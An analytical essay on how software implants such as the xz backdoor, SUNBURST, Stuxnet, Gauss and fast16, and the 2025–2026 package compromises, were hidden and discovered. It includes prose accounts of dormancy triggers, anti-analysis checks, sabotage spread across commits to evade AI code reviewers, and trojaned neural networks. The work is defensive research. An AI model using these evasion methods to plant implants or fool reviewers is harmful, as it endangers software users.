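A release cannot always be compared with its repository. In 2011, attackers replaced the release of vsFTPd, a file-transfer server, with one that opened a root shell (a command line with full control) to anyone whose user name contained ":)". Kokkonis and colleagues could find no Git history for vsFTPd. Without a repository, a reviewer could have compared the altered release only with the previous one, and would have had to read 1,407 changed lines in five files. Lily's report reduced this to seven lines in one file.

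### Malice that somebody properly committed

Neither comparison helps if an attacker gets a malicious change accepted into the main repository. In the 2003 Linux discussion, the developer Theodore Ts'o wrote that an attacker could forge an email from a trusted developer and hide the harmful lines among plausible changes in a patch presented as a bug fix. Ts'o wanted every change to be digitally signed, which would expose the forgery but would not help against someone like Jia Tan, who had earned the right to commit.

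Only reading or running the code can catch such a change, but participants at an industry meeting agreed that it is very hard to judge intent from a single commit (*S3C2 Summit 2025-09*, 2026). They suggested also considering the contributor's history and having two people review each change. Both suggestions seem sensible, but Jia Tan had a good history for two years, and a second reviewer can miss "= 0" as easily as the first.

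### AI reviewers in 2026

One of the main weaknesses of source review is that nobody has time to read everything, and many projects now remove it by having AI systems review incoming code. *CyberDual* (Yang, Lee and colleagues, 2026) tested how well these reviewers handle deliberate sabotage. AI attackers planted memory errors in 14 widely used C and C++ libraries, including xz, and wrote an input that exploited each error. AI reviewers then had to find and repair the error without seeing that input. The test counted an attack as caught if the exploit no longer worked afterwards.

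Of 1,088 working attacks, Anthropic's Sonnet 5 caught 85%, its Opus 4.8 caught 88% and OpenAI's GPT-6-Sol caught 91%. The attacker's starting material made a large difference. The percentages below are the shares of attacks that still worked after review:

| What the attacker had | Attacks | Sonnet 5 | Opus 4.8 | GPT-6-Sol |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| One task | 349 | 2.3% | 1.1% | 0.0% |
| One task and the project's real fix to imitate | 312 | 13.9% | 13.3% | 5.4% |
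| 50 to 199 real commits to alter | 427 | 24.4% | 17.1% | 19.4% |

In the hardest setting, the attackers usually spread an error over several commits. In the image library OpenEXR, one altered commit made a table grow only as needed and checked lookups against the table's current size. A later commit changed the check to use a different, larger count. Each change looked reasonable alone, but together they let the program read past the end of the table. Attackers also lied in commit messages. In xz, one attacker removed a safety step and later cited that step as the reason another part of the code was safe.

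Yang and colleagues tested Sonnet 5 on some of these attacks again, showing it only the altered commits and the commits that depended on them. It caught 90%, compared with 80% when it read the full history. The Linux readers in 2003 had the same advantage, since McVoy had shown them exactly which lines to examine. In normal use, reviewers don't have this advantage because nobody knows which commits are the attacker's.

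Using several reviewers helps considerably, since only 28 of the 1,088 attacks got past all three. GPT-6-Sol also did somewhat better than you would expect from its score. In 79 of its 100 misses it rejected the change but then repaired the wrong code, so a project that refused rejected changes would have been safe from those attacks. However, 71 of the 79 were in the long histories, where refusing everything would mean discarding dozens of genuine commits by other people.

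Other kinds of attack are harder to catch. In *PRWeaver*, Wang, Cheng and Xie (2026) planted 208 attacks in ten projects, most of them Python web software. Many broke rules about what users may do, such as how they may use a shop's gift cards. Six combinations of review tool and model detected 50 to 60% of the attacks when they reviewed each pull request (a proposed set of changes) separately, but only 16 to 22% when they reviewed 24 together. Splitting an attack into pieces changed the detection rate by at most five percentage points. Combining each piece with a genuine change and writing a description that plausibly covered both lowered the rate by 10 to 18 points. Detection rates were lower than in *CyberDual*, perhaps because a memory error can crash a test program, whereas a web shop that wrongly accepts a gift card runs normally.

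Maintainers also need to know how often a reviewer raises false alarms. *MOSAIC-Bench* (2026) tested Gemma-4-E4B, a small, freely available model, by prompting it to review code as a penetration tester (someone hired to break into systems). It detected 88.4% of 199 planted vulnerabilities, each built up over a series of changes, and wrongly flagged 4.6% of 608 real pull requests, at about a tenth of a cent per review. The larger Sonnet 4.6 detected 97.0% of the vulnerabilities, at about 18 cents per review. None of the attackers in the test had practiced against these reviewers. A real attacker could practice against Gemma, since anyone can run it at home.

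Suppose one pull request in 10,000 is malicious. At Gemma's rates, a project that received 10,000 requests would get about 460 false alarms and would probably catch the malicious one. Most maintainers would find checking those alarms tiresome, but it is far less work than reading all 10,000 requests equally closely.

AI reviewers can also examine compiled programs, which matters when the source code is clean or secret. Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026), in *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries*, gave models standard reverse engineering tools and asked them to find planted backdoors. On the accompanying leaderboard, Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, the best models succeeded in 49% of attempts. One of these, Gemini 3.1 Pro, wrongly flagged 17% of clean programs, while a version of GPT-5.2 succeeded in 46% of attempts with no false alarms. These models date from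 early 2026 or before, so current ones may well do better.

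## Which implants show no anomaly before they act?

In the invented login story, the administrator noticed the backdoor only because somebody used it. Until then, the heron-4471 line had not slowed the program down, crashed it or sent any traffic. Real implants vary in how close they come to this. An observer might notice any of three things:

- **The cost of being present.** This is whatever the implant uses up or disturbs once someone has installed it.
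- **The cost of checking for the trigger.** The implant has to find out somehow whether the time to act has come.
- **The effects of the payload.**

An implant shows no anomaly before it acts if the costs of presence and checking are too small for anyone to notice.

### Two weeks of waiting

SUNBURST, the backdoor in SolarWinds's Orion software, put off contacting its operators until several conditions held. According to FireEye, these included the following:

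1. The backdoor was running inside the right Orion program.
2. At least 12 to 14 days had passed since the file containing it was last written. The backdoor picked the exact limit at random.
3. The computer belonged to a Windows domain, the kind of centrally managed network that companies use.
4. No program or driver on the computer matched the backdoor's lists of security and analysis tools.
5. The computer could look up SolarWinds's own internet address, which showed that it was online.

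If the backdoor found a listed tool, it stopped and tried again later. It stored the lists as hashes, fixed-length numbers calculated from the names, so an analyst could not simply read which products it avoided. FireEye recovered some of the names by guessing.

A careful customer who tested each update on a spare machine for a week would have missed the implant because of its waiting period. An analyst who knew about the wait could have set the computer's clock forward, but the machine would still have had to meet the other conditions. A laboratory machine could easily fail them, since it runs analysis tools and may not belong to a company's domain.

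Once the conditions held, SUNBURST looked up a domain name whose first part encoded the name of the victim's network. This let the operators choose which victims to pursue. If the lookup returned an IP address within certain ranges, the backdoor shut down permanently. Many of these ranges belong to private networks, and CISA's *Advanced Persistent Threat Compromise of Government Agencies* interprets the check as an attempt to detect an analysis environment. Defenders used this condition to disable the backdoor, and by December 15, 2020, the operators' domain pointed to a Microsoft address within one of the ranges.

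Some of this behavior was visible. SUNBURST changed Windows settings to disable certain security services, which an attentive administrator could have noticed. The backdoor also spaced its lookups irregularly, from a minute to nine hours apart, but they had to leave the computer, so a customer who logged every lookup would have had a record of them.

That record did not show whether anyone had used the backdoor. CISA warned customers who found only the initial lookups not to assume that the intruders had gone further. A reply that directed the backdoor to a second domain was much more worrying. CISA's instructions also covered networks that had the malicious file but had made no lookups.

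### Stuxnet's list of equipment

The version of Stuxnet found in 2010 spread widely, but its payload needed equipment that few places had. According to Symantec, it required a Siemens S7-300 controller with a particular communications module, connected to frequency converters from specific manufacturers. The converters had to be running at 807 to 1,210 hertz. If a rotor turns once per cycle, that is about 48,000 to 73,000 revolutions per minute, a range that includes the 63,000 for which the Natanz centrifuges were designed. Symantec's Eric Chien, quoted by the Institute for Science and International Security, said the converters had to run at these frequencies for some time before Stuxnet took over the controller.

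In other factories, Stuxnet's payload did nothing. OTbase credits this to the attackers' care in matching the attack to one configuration, which they apparently had a copy of. An engineer at another factory could have watched the controllers indefinitely without seeing any sign of the worm, even if it was on every Windows computer in the building.

The earlier version was harder to notice. In 2007, somebody submitted a copy to VirusTotal, a website that scans files with many antivirus programs, and no antivirus company recognized it. On a controller at Natanz, it did little for weeks except analyze the state of the plant. When it attacked, it also changed the calibration of pressure gauges in the centrifuge hall so that their displays would show normal values to anyone walking past.

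### Triggers that an analyst cannot supply

An analyst can get the password from the heron-4471 line and learn from Stuxnet's checks what equipment to buy for a test. But the xz attackers made their backdoor run only commands signed with their private key. The backdoor contained only the matching public key, which can check a signature but not make one, so an analyst who understood every instruction still could not use it on somebody else's server. On a test machine, the analyst could replace the public key with a new one and sign commands with the matching private key.

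The backdoor was slow to start, but its check for the signature caused little disturbance. Freund traced a login that used a key and saw it enter the backdoor's code, which then called the normal cryptographic library, presumably to authenticate the login as usual. The attackers also didn't need the server to contact them, because they could send it the trigger in a login attempt.

Gauss, a spyware program discovered in 2012, hides its payload as well as its trigger. Kaspersky found it through its similarities to Flame, another spyware program, and recorded more than 2,500 infections, mostly in the Middle East. Some of the files that Gauss puts on USB sticks contain encrypted code. Kaspersky's *The Mystery of the Encrypted Gauss Payload* describes how Gauss tries to decrypt it on each computer:

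1. Gauss lists the folders in Path, a Windows setting that records where to look for programs.
2. It adds any names in the Program Files folder that start with a character numbered higher than "z". These could be names in Arabic or Hebrew, or names that start with a symbol such as "~".
3. It forms every possible pair of entries from this list. To each pair it adds 16 fixed bytes, then calculates a hash and hashes the result another 10,000 times.
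4. If the outcome matches a value stored in Gauss, it repeats the process on the same pair with 16 different bytes. It uses that result to make the decryption key.

The key is therefore not in the file. The stored value can confirm a correct guess, but nobody can feasibly recover the pair of names from it. On the wrong computer, neither Gauss nor anyone studying it can decrypt the payload.

Quarkslab (2012) traces this idea to a 1998 paper by Riordan and Schneier on programs that must run on untrusted machines. Quarkslab contrasts Gauss with Stuxnet, whose payload any analyst with a copy could read. Stuxnet's list of equipment helped analysts identify Natanz as the target, but from Gauss they can learn only that its target has a program with an unusual folder name.

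Kaspersky tried millions of combinations of known names without success. If the folder name has 12 letters from the 28-letter Arabic alphabet, there are about 2.3 × 10^17 possible names. Even if an analyst already knew the Path entry, a machine testing a million names a second would need about 7,400 years to try them all, although someone who thought of the right program could confirm it at once. Quarkslab thought the encrypted parts all unlocked together, so one correct pair would probably reveal the whole payload.

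As of December 2026, nobody appears to have published a decryption of the Gauss payload. In December 2012, Jens Steube, who wrote the password-recovery program hashcat, released a free tool that used graphics processors to speed up the guessing. Kaspersky's *Hashcat’s GPU-accelerated Gauss encryption cracker* (2012) still listed the payload among the year's unsolved mysteries. In *What ever happened with Gauss?* (2020), a post on hashcat's forum, abc882 asked whether someone had cracked it and kept quiet, which remains possible.

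### What was left to notice

| Implant | Cost of being present | Cost of checking for the trigger | Effects of the payload |
|---|---|---|---|
| heron-4471 (invented) | Almost none | One comparison per login | A session that looks like any other |
| xz | Half a second of processor time at each start of sshd; Valgrind errors | A signature check during some logins | Whatever the attacker's command did |
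| SUNBURST | An altered file with a valid signature | Internet lookups; disabled security services | Stolen credentials and further intrusions |
| Stuxnet (2010 version) | A spreading worm; probably crashes | Queries about controllers and motor speeds | Changed rotor speeds |
| Gauss's encrypted payload | Unreadable data in files on USB sticks | Perhaps a second or two of hashing | Unknown |

The Gauss estimate assumes 20 names on the list, which make 400 pairs and require about four million hash calculations. Those calculations may take more processor time than the xz backdoor used at each start. But the xz backdoor repeated its work for every connection to a server that should have been idle, while a short delay after someone plugs in a USB stick is easy to ignore.

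Better programming could have removed most of the overhead that the xz backdoor added just by being present. Its signature check would have remained but been very hard to notice, leaving only the effects of the attacker's commands to detect. SUNBURST's lookups were harder to avoid because its operators wanted to choose among their victims after infecting them, so the backdoor had to contact them for instructions. Checking for a trigger is much less noticeable when the trigger is already on the computer or arrives in the input.

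### The arithmetic of clean tests

Testers can look for a dormant implant by running the program under many different conditions and checking whether it misbehaves. If each random test independently has probability *p* of meeting the trigger condition, the probability that *n* tests all miss it is (1 − *p*)^*n*.

If all *n* tests are clean, *p* could still be above zero, but a large *p* would make such a result unlikely. The usual 95% upper bound is the value of *p* at which the chance of a clean result falls to 5%:

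(1 − *p*)^*n* = 0.05

Taking natural logarithms gives *n* ln(1 − *p*) = ln 0.05, which is about −3. When *p* is small, ln(1 − *p*) is close to −*p*, so the bound is about 3/*n*.

For example, testers replay 3,000 logins drawn at random from a company's records, and the login program handles all of them correctly. The upper bound on the share of logins that meet a trigger is 3/3,000, or 0.1%. If one login in 1,000 did meet a trigger, the chance that none of the 3,000 would is 0.999^3,000, or about 5%, so the testers can be fairly confident that ordinary logins meet a trigger less often than that. In a company with 500,000 logins a year, though, up to 500 could still meet one.

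This is useful for judging an accidental fault, because users will run into it about as often as testers do, but an attacker who knows the trigger can produce the fault every time. A tester who tries a million random ten-character passwords and sees nothing unusual gets an upper bound of three in a million on the chance that a random password is the trigger. The real chance of hitting heron-4471 is one in 4.8 quadrillion, about 14 billion times smaller, and neither number measures how often the attacker will type it. Random testing is far less likely still to produce the signature that xz required.

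Hidden conditions also undermine the assumption that the tests are independent. If the testers run all 3,000 tests in the week after installing an update, SUNBURST's waiting period will keep it inactive in every one, and another 3,000 tests that week would add no information. Likewise, someone could have examined 100,000 computers infected with Stuxnet outside Natanz, found no attack on a controller and calculated a bound of three in 100,000. That bound might be correct, but the attackers needed Stuxnet to act at only one plant.

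Testers can do better by choosing their tests. Some fuzzing tools track the comparisons a program makes, so they could copy heron-4471 from the doctored line. An analyst can also build a lab that meets a known list of conditions, as Langner's team did with Siemens equipment. Neither approach produces the xz attackers' signature or the folder names that unlock Gauss. Triggers in neural networks raise a similar problem.

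### Does a quiet implant have to act?

A perfectly quiet implant might not seem very worrying, because it is useless to the attacker until it acts, and acting gives the defender something to notice. The SolarWinds case supports this view, since the intruders' use of an employee's account led FireEye to discover SUNBURST.

Repetition is a serious problem for a spy who wants new documents every week, because each action gives the defender another chance to notice. If each action has a 1% chance of being noticed, independently of the others, the spy has only about a 5% chance of carrying out 300 actions unnoticed.

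But a single action has a 99% chance of going undetected, and one may be enough. A single command sent through the xz backdoor could have copied a server's secret keys or erased its disks. Noticing the command afterwards would not restore the erased data. An attacker who stole credentials could also log in with them from then on and stop using the backdoor.

An attacker who relies on one action gets no chance to correct a mistake. The SolarWinds intruders rehearsed in a real build, which gave the company an earlier opportunity to catch them. Other attackers can rehearse in private. For example, OTbase argues that Stuxnet's makers must have had a working group of centrifuges filled with real uranium gas.

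Even an implant that acts repeatedly may go unnoticed if its effects look like something else. SentinelOne's *fast16* (2026) describes a sabotage program from 2005 that altered the results of engineering calculations. By default, the program did not install itself on a computer where it found any of 18 security products. It modified only programs that carried a mark left by Intel's compiler, and it searched them without slowing the computer much.

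Symantec's *Fast16* confirmed that fast16's targets included LS-DYNA and AUTODYN, two programs that can simulate explosions. According to Zetter Zero Day's *Experts Confirm the Fast16 Malware Was Sabotaging Nuclear Weapons Tests, Likely in Iran*, the malware acted only when the density of a simulated uranium core reached 30 grams per cubic centimeter. It then replaced the results with false ones suggesting that the explosives had not compressed the core enough. The physicist David Albright said that engineers would probably not have seen anything unusual in values that were 1 to 5% too low, and would have blamed their design.

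Repeating the calculation on a clean computer would have exposed the difference. But fast16 copied itself to other computers on the same network, so a second machine there would probably have given the same wrong answer. It is unclear whether the victims ever discovered it.

Researchers discovered fast16 from a stored copy, not from its effects. The name appeared in a leaked NSA tool in 2017, and someone uploaded a copy of the program to VirusTotal that October. Juan Andres Guerrero-Saade of SentinelOne found that copy in 2019. SentinelOne says its researchers had been searching old malware for traces of Lua, a scripting language that several advanced spying tools contain. Guerrero-Saade and Vitaly Kamluk tried for years to work out what the program did and succeeded only after they turned to AI. When they published their findings in April 2026, only one of VirusTotal's scanners flagged the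 file as malicious, with limited confidence.

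## What can be inferred from the implants that were found?

Five of the cases left enough evidence to compare each step of the discovery.

| Implant | First signal | Who saw it | What located the implant | What proved malice | Dwell time |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| xz | Unexplained processor use | Andres Freund, while measuring database speed | A profiler, then a comparison of slow and fast runs | Reading the build script and the hidden code | 33 days |
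| Stuxnet | Repeated reboots | A VirusBlokAda customer in Iran | Examining an infected computer | Reverse engineering | Just under a year |
| SolarWinds | A second phone on an employee's account | FireEye's security staff | A forensic trail to one server, then decompiling Orion | Reverse engineering | At least 263 days |
| Triangulation | Odd connections from iPhones | Kaspersky staff monitoring the office Wi-Fi | Phone backups matched to the Wi-Fi records | Reverse engineering of captured code | At least three years |
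| Linux, 2003 | Two copies of a file that differed | BitMover's nightly check | The same check | Source review by readers of a mailing list | Probably about a day |

A runtime anomaly was the first signal in four of the five cases. The table contains only implants that somebody found, so we can't infer from it that most implants cause an anomaly sooner or later, or that a careful observer will catch them.

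The record does support a more modest inference. In all five cases, somebody had to read source code, a build script or decompiler output to prove malice. This would probably hold for undiscovered implants too, because showing what a program was built to do more or less requires reading it, however the search began.

### The share of discoveries and the chance of discovery

Anomalies led people to four of the five implants in the table, but the table includes only implants that were discovered. Drawing conclusions about all implants from these five would be survivorship bias, the mistake of judging a whole group by the members that got through some filter. A company deciding how far to rely on anomaly detection needs to know what share of all planted implants cause an anomaly that somebody follows up, and that share can be very different from four in five.

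In a hypothetical population of 1,000 implants, 200 are noisy, meaning they cause a noticeable anomaly, and 800 are quiet. Over ten years, defenders find half of the noisy ones by following up the anomalies, and one in 40 of the quiet ones through code review, comparisons or luck.

| | Noisy | Quiet | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Planted | 200 | 800 | 1,000 |
| Discovered | 100 | 20 | 120 |
| Still hidden | 100 | 780 | 880 |

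In this example, quiet implants outnumber noisy ones four to one and make up 89% of those still hidden, but 83% of the 120 discovered implants were noisy. Anyone who studies only the discovered implants may well conclude that quiet ones are rare. Anomalies led to 83% of the discoveries but exposed only 10% of all the implants.

The general rule is short. If a share *s* of all implants is noisy, and defenders find a noisy implant with probability *a* and a quiet one with probability *b*, the ratio of noisy to quiet implants among the discoveries is

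*s* / (1 − *s*) × *a* / *b*

In the example this is 1/4 × 20, or five to one. The calculation also works backwards. Suppose that the real record contains four noisy implants for every quiet one, as the five cases roughly suggest:

| How many times likelier defenders are to find a noisy implant than a quiet one | Share of all implants that are noisy |
|---|---|
| 1 (equally likely) | 80% |
| 4 | 50% |
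| 20 | 17% |
| 100 | 4% |

Every row fits the five cases equally well. Choosing between the rows requires knowing how often quiet implants go undiscovered, and nobody can work that out from discoveries alone. Quiet implants are harder to find, so the real share of noisy ones is probably lower than the record suggests, though how much lower is less clear.

Fame makes this worse, because the five cases are well known partly for how people found them. An engineer who investigates half a second of processor time makes a better news story than a scheduled job that compares checksums.

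### Changes that reviewers turned away

The record also omits many of the defenders' successes. When a maintainer receives a suspicious patch from a stranger, the easiest response is to decline it. The maintainer seldom has proof of malice, and no user ran the code, so nobody has much reason to write about it. The PHP backdoor made the news because it had already entered the main repository. If a reviewer had rejected the same lines in a proposed change, few people would have heard of them.

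Suppose attackers in the example made 1,500 attempts, and reviewers rejected 500 of them, leaving the 1,000 implants. If five of the rejections become public, the record will contain 125 cases, and reviewers will have kept the implant out in only 4% of them, although they rejected a third of all attempts.

Survivorship bias makes defenders look better than they are, while the lack of records of rejected changes has the opposite effect, and no one can calculate the net result. An undiscovered implant has escaped both source review and anomaly detection, so the hidden cases do not clearly favor either method. But anyone who ranks the methods by counting famous discoveries will almost certainly underrate source review.

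### Two implants in a public collection

Researchers sometimes recognize an implant many years late, and these cases provide some information about the implants that are still hidden. Somebody uploaded the earliest known version of Stuxnet to VirusTotal on November 15, 2007. Symantec recognized it about five years later, during a routine search of its own malware database for files that matched known patterns, and announced the discovery in February 2013.

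By then analysts had been studying the later versions for more than two years. They already suspected that an earlier version existed, because the attackers had labeled the June 2009 version 1.001. The 2007 version turned out to be 0.5. It had limited ways to spread, which is probably one reason nobody caught it at the time. If the attackers had never released the more aggressive versions, Symantec would have had no Stuxnet patterns to search for.

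Version 0.5 also produced a visible symptom. It installed a driver that forced the computer to restart with a blue screen 20 days after infection. Unsurprisingly, nobody is known to have traced any of those restarts to the worm, since people rarely investigate a single crash on a Windows computer. The machines that Sergey Ulasen heard about in 2010, by contrast, crashed repeatedly.

The forced restart raised the possibility that version 0.5 was also on those machines in 2010 and had caused the reboots. Symantec's Liam O Murchu thought VirusBlokAda was unlikely to have missed a second version.

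fast16, the program that falsified simulations of nuclear explosions, stayed hidden for much longer, and more than 20 years passed between its creation and the first public analysis. SentinelOne explains that its search for old uses of Lua relied on distinctive bytes that the language leaves in a file. One of the results looked like an ordinary Windows service, but it contained a leftover file path with the name fast16, which connected it to the leaked NSA tool.

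Users may have noticed anomalies in the simulations that fast16 falsified. Symantec found that fast16's rules for altering programs fell into up to ten groups, each written for a different build of the simulation software. The attackers apparently added the rules for one older version after those for a newer one. Symantec suggests that a user who saw strange results went back to the older version, and that the attackers then targeted that version too. Symantec acknowledges that the evidence is thin. If the suggestion is right, the user noticed a runtime anomaly, reasonably treated it as a software bug, and did not find the implant.

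Researchers recognized both programs because each resembled something they already knew, as Kaspersky had with Gauss. Searching old collections therefore mostly adds relatives of known implants to the record. It is much less likely to find an implant that has an original design and whose makers were never caught with anything else, and it can't find a file that nobody ever uploaded. SentinelOne suspects that collections still hold other important tools, filed as old but interesting samples that no one has had the context to understand.

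### Dwell times in 2025

Statistics on recent break-ins have the same gap. Mandiant's *M-Trends 2026 Report* (2026) covers attacks the company investigated in 2025. Many involved stolen passwords or ransomware, which locks a victim's data until the victim pays, so the figures describe intrusions in general, not only implants.

| Cases investigated | Dwell time |
|---|---|
| All | Median of 14 days, up from 11 in 2024 |
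| Espionage | Median of 122 days |
| North Korean IT workers inside companies | Median of 122 days |
| Attacks using the backdoor BRICKSTORM | Average of 393 days |

The BRICKSTORM figure is an average, which a few very long cases can raise, so it isn't strictly comparable with the medians.

Victims first detected the activity themselves in 52% of the investigations. They first learned of it from a third party in 34% and from the attackers in the remaining 14%. In ransomware cases, the attackers told the victim 44% of the time. Extortionists have to contact the victim to get paid, which ends the dwell time, while spies have every reason to stay silent. The overall median of 14 days is therefore a poor guide to how long an implant stays hidden when its makers want it to last. The median for espionage cases is a closer comparison, and it falls between the 33 days for the xz backdoor and the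 263 days for SUNBURST.

All these figures leave out undiscovered intrusions. Suppose that defenders find 100 intrusions after a median of 14 days and never find another 100. The median for all 200 would be at least as long as the longest dwell time among the 100 they found. A rise in the published median can be good news if investigators have started to find old intrusions they used to miss. Mandiant attributes the latest rise largely to espionage and North Korean IT workers, but we can't tell from its figures whether those attackers became more common or just easier to find.

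Long dwell times are also the hardest to measure. Many organizations keep their logs for 90 days, so by the time somebody finds an intruder who arrived 393 days ago, the evidence of how they got in is usually gone. Kutscher (2026), in *M-Trends 2026*, adds that attackers run BRICKSTORM in the memory of network devices that have little storage and can't run ordinary security software. Investigators find few traces there. In cases like these, the earliest surviving trace may date from long after the intrusion began.

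### Package compromises of 2025 and 2026

A sample is less selective if its cases are chosen for a reason unrelated to how people found them. The major compromises of open-source packages in 2025 and 2026 are a reasonable choice, because they became news for the number of users at risk. This sample still includes only compromises that were discovered.

The first compromise was that of tj-actions/changed-files, a ready-made step that more than 23,000 repositories used in their automatic builds and tests. On March 14, 2025, at 16:57 UTC according to *tj-action/changed-files GitHub action was compromised* (Esler, 2025), an attacker pointed all 361 of its labeled versions to malicious code that printed passwords and keys into the build logs. *Harden-Runner detection* (Sharma, 2025) reported the same day that a monitoring tool from the security company StepSecurity had detected an unexpected address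 in a build's network traffic. The address was apparently one of GitHub's own, where anyone can post snippets of text. It would look harmless on a list of addresses, but builds that used this step did not normally contact it.

In September 2025, an attacker tricked the developer Josh Junon with a fake security email and published backdoored versions of his JavaScript packages, including the popular chalk and debug. Charlie Eriksen, a security researcher, warned Junon about an hour after the first bad releases (fasterthanli.me, *color npm package compromised*, 2025). One of the first public signals was a failed build, according to Jscrambler's *The npm chalk and debug attack proves again*. The build failed because the attacker's code called a function missing from older versions of Node.js, which runs JavaScript outside a browser. It is unclear whether that error alerted Eriksen.

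Later that month, a worm called Shai-Hulud spread from one npm package to the next. A developer named Daniel Pereira seems to have raised the first alarm, and several others noticed the worm at about the same time. It is hard to establish what any of them saw first.

LiteLLM, a library for using AI models from many companies, is the clearest case of an implant found through an anomaly. FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026) explains that the malicious version contained a file that ran whenever Python started. The file launched a second copy of Python, which ran the file again, in an endless loop the attackers had not intended. A timeline from FutureSearch (2026) puts the upload at 10:52 UTC on March 24 and the forced restart of an engineer's laptop at 11:09, after about 11,000 processes had started. Another user, dot_treo, reported in *Tell HN* running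 out of memory while setting up a new project and independently finding malicious code. The attackers had uploaded a different malicious version 13 minutes before 1.82.8, and FutureSearch added it to its warning only at 12:30.

A week later, attackers took over the account of a maintainer of axios, a JavaScript package with about 100 million downloads a week. This time, software that reads code detected the attack first. The attackers had put the payload in a second package, plain-crypto-js. *Supply Chain Attack on Axios Pulls Malicious Dependency from npm* (Socket, 2026) reports that Socket's scanner flagged this package at 00:05 UTC on March 31, within six minutes of its publication. *Compromised axios npm package delivers cross-platform RAT* (Tafani-Dereeper, 2026) reports that the first malicious version of axios appeared at 00:21, 16 minutes after the scanner flagged the payload. The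 malicious versions still stayed available for about three hours.

*Behind the Scenes* (Sharma, 2026) describes how StepSecurity also caught the new axios release by automated analysis. One sign was that the release depended on a package that none of its code used. StepSecurity's network monitor then detected build machines contacting an unfamiliar server, which confirmed the finding before anyone had looked at the code. When the company posted warnings on the project's GitHub page, the attackers deleted them about 20 times.

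| Compromise | First known signal | Route | Time from malicious release to signal |
|---|---|---|---|
| tj-actions | Unfamiliar address in a build's traffic | Runtime anomaly | Less than a day |
| chalk and debug | Possibly a failed build | Unclear | About an hour at most |
| Shai-Hulud | Reports from developers | Unclear | Unclear |
| LiteLLM | Laptops running out of memory | Runtime anomaly | 17 minutes or less |
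| axios | Automated scan of a dependency | Source review by software | Six minutes |

Anomalies clearly came first in two of these five package compromises, compared with four of the five famous cases. The difference is suggestive at most. Even if the package compromises were a random sample, the 95% confidence interval for the true share would run from about 5% to 85%. Much of the evidence comes from companies describing the success of products they sell, although the times of the axios releases come from npm's own records.

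Integrity checks could have caught at least two of the compromises. Neither the malicious LiteLLM version nor the malicious axios versions had a matching release on the project's GitHub page. Tafani-Dereeper also found in npm's public records that an automated GitHub process had published the previous version of axios, while the malicious one came directly from the maintainer's account, whose email address had changed.

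Several of the attackers made basic programming errors, including the runaway processes in LiteLLM and the missing function in the chalk and debug attack. The axios payload also crashed on Linux in the kind of environment where automated builds run, and its Windows script never called its own main function. Errors like these cause many of the anomalies in the record, so the implants in it may mostly be the work of attackers who didn't test their code carefully.

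In the tj-actions case, as with Stuxnet, investigators found a narrow attack because a broad one followed it. Unit 42's *GitHub Actions Supply Chain Attack* traced the campaign to November 2024, about four months before anyone noticed. The attackers moved through two other open-source projects and at first targeted only the cryptocurrency company Coinbase. They prepared the malicious code in copies of the repositories under throwaway accounts, and they changed version labels, a step GitHub does not log for projects on its free plan. At 15:10 UTC on March 14, they obtained a key that let them change one of Coinbase's projects. Less than two hours later, they attacked everyone who used tj-actions, and people noticed that attack. If they had stopped at Coinbase, the campaign might well be missing from this sample.

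All five compromises started stealing or spreading as soon as someone installed or ran the package, on a very large number of machines. Attackers who work this way expect to be caught and try to take as much as possible first. An implant planted in a little-used package in the same months, and still waiting for one particular company to install it, would not be in the sample yet. The short times in the table are therefore good evidence that defenders now catch mass attacks quickly, but almost no evidence about attacks that wait for a particular target.

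### Estimating how many remain

Capture-recapture, a method biologists use to estimate how many fish are in a lake, could in principle also estimate the number of undiscovered implants. Biologists catch some fish, mark them, put them back and later catch a second batch. The share of marked fish in the second batch roughly equals the share of the whole population they caught the first time.

Suppose one team searches a collection of software and finds 60 implants. A second team searches the same collection and finds 40, of which 24 are also on the first team's list. The first team found 60% of the implants the second team found. If it also found 60% of all the implants in the collection, there must be 100. The two teams together found 76 different implants, so about 24 would remain undiscovered. In general, if the teams find *n*₁ and *n*₂ implants and *m* are on both lists, the estimated total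 is *n*₁ × *n*₂ / *m*.

The estimate is only as good as its assumptions:

- Both teams search the same software, and nobody adds or removes implants in the meantime.
- Neither team's discoveries influence the other's.
- Any one team is about equally likely to find each of the implants.
- The teams can tell when they have found the same implant.

Publicity quickly breaks the rule about influence, because when a company announces an implant, others search for it. After Pereira's warning about Shai-Hulud, Socket identified 40 infected packages, and another security company, Aikido, then found 147 more. Because Aikido was adding to an existing list, the overlap between the two lists can't be used to make an estimate.

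The assumption that all implants are equally likely to be found is a more serious problem, because it reintroduces survivorship bias. Even independent searchers tend to find the same noisy implants and miss the same quiet ones. Two people found the LiteLLM attack independently, for example, but both did so because their computers ran out of memory.

The invented population of 200 noisy and 800 quiet implants shows how large the error can be. If two teams search it independently, and each finds half of the noisy implants and one in 40 of the quiet ones, each team finds 120. On average, 50 noisy implants and 0.5 quiet ones are found by both teams, so the estimated total is 120 × 120 / 50.5, or about 285, when the true number is 1,000. The teams would conclude that between them they had found well over half of the implants, when they had found less than a fifth.

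Estimating the noisy and quiet implants separately works only for the noisy ones, where 100 × 100 / 50 gives the correct answer of 200. For the quiet ones, each team has a list of about 20. About 60% of the time the lists have nothing in common, so the formula divides by zero and gives no answer. If they share one implant, the estimate is 400, half the true number. The teams would have to find far more quiet implants for the method to work, but they needed the method because quiet implants are hard to find.

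A package registry is probably the best place to try this. Several companies already scan new releases on npm, so they could timestamp each discovery and not share their findings with one another until all of them had finished. But withholding a warning about live malware for even an hour would put users at risk, so the companies would have to send their findings at once to a neutral party that could remove the package. The result would still cover only the kinds of implant that at least one scanner can detect.

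The total number of implants in real software is unknown, but researchers who plant their own, as in Lily and *CyberDual*, know exactly how many there are. They can therefore measure how often a method detects a given kind of implant, which is impossible from the historical record. However, the implants they choose may be easier to find than the ones real attackers have kept hidden.

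## Does the software record carry over to neural networks?

The software cases suggest an argument about trojaned models, the neural networks with a planted backdoor:

1. Odd behavior exposed most of the known implants in software.
2. Source review missed them because the systems were too large to read closely, or because reviewers read something other than the code that ran.
3. Neural networks are even harder to read than source code.
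4. Odd behavior is therefore the better hope for finding implants in networks too.

The first premise is true of the famous cases, but only of the first signal, and only among implants that somebody found. It supports the conclusion only if the causes of the odd behavior also exist in networks. The xz backdoor was slow because of the way it disguised function names, and the malicious LiteLLM release exhausted laptops' memory because of a programming mistake. An implant in a network's weights has no function names to look up and no program code that could contain such a mistake.

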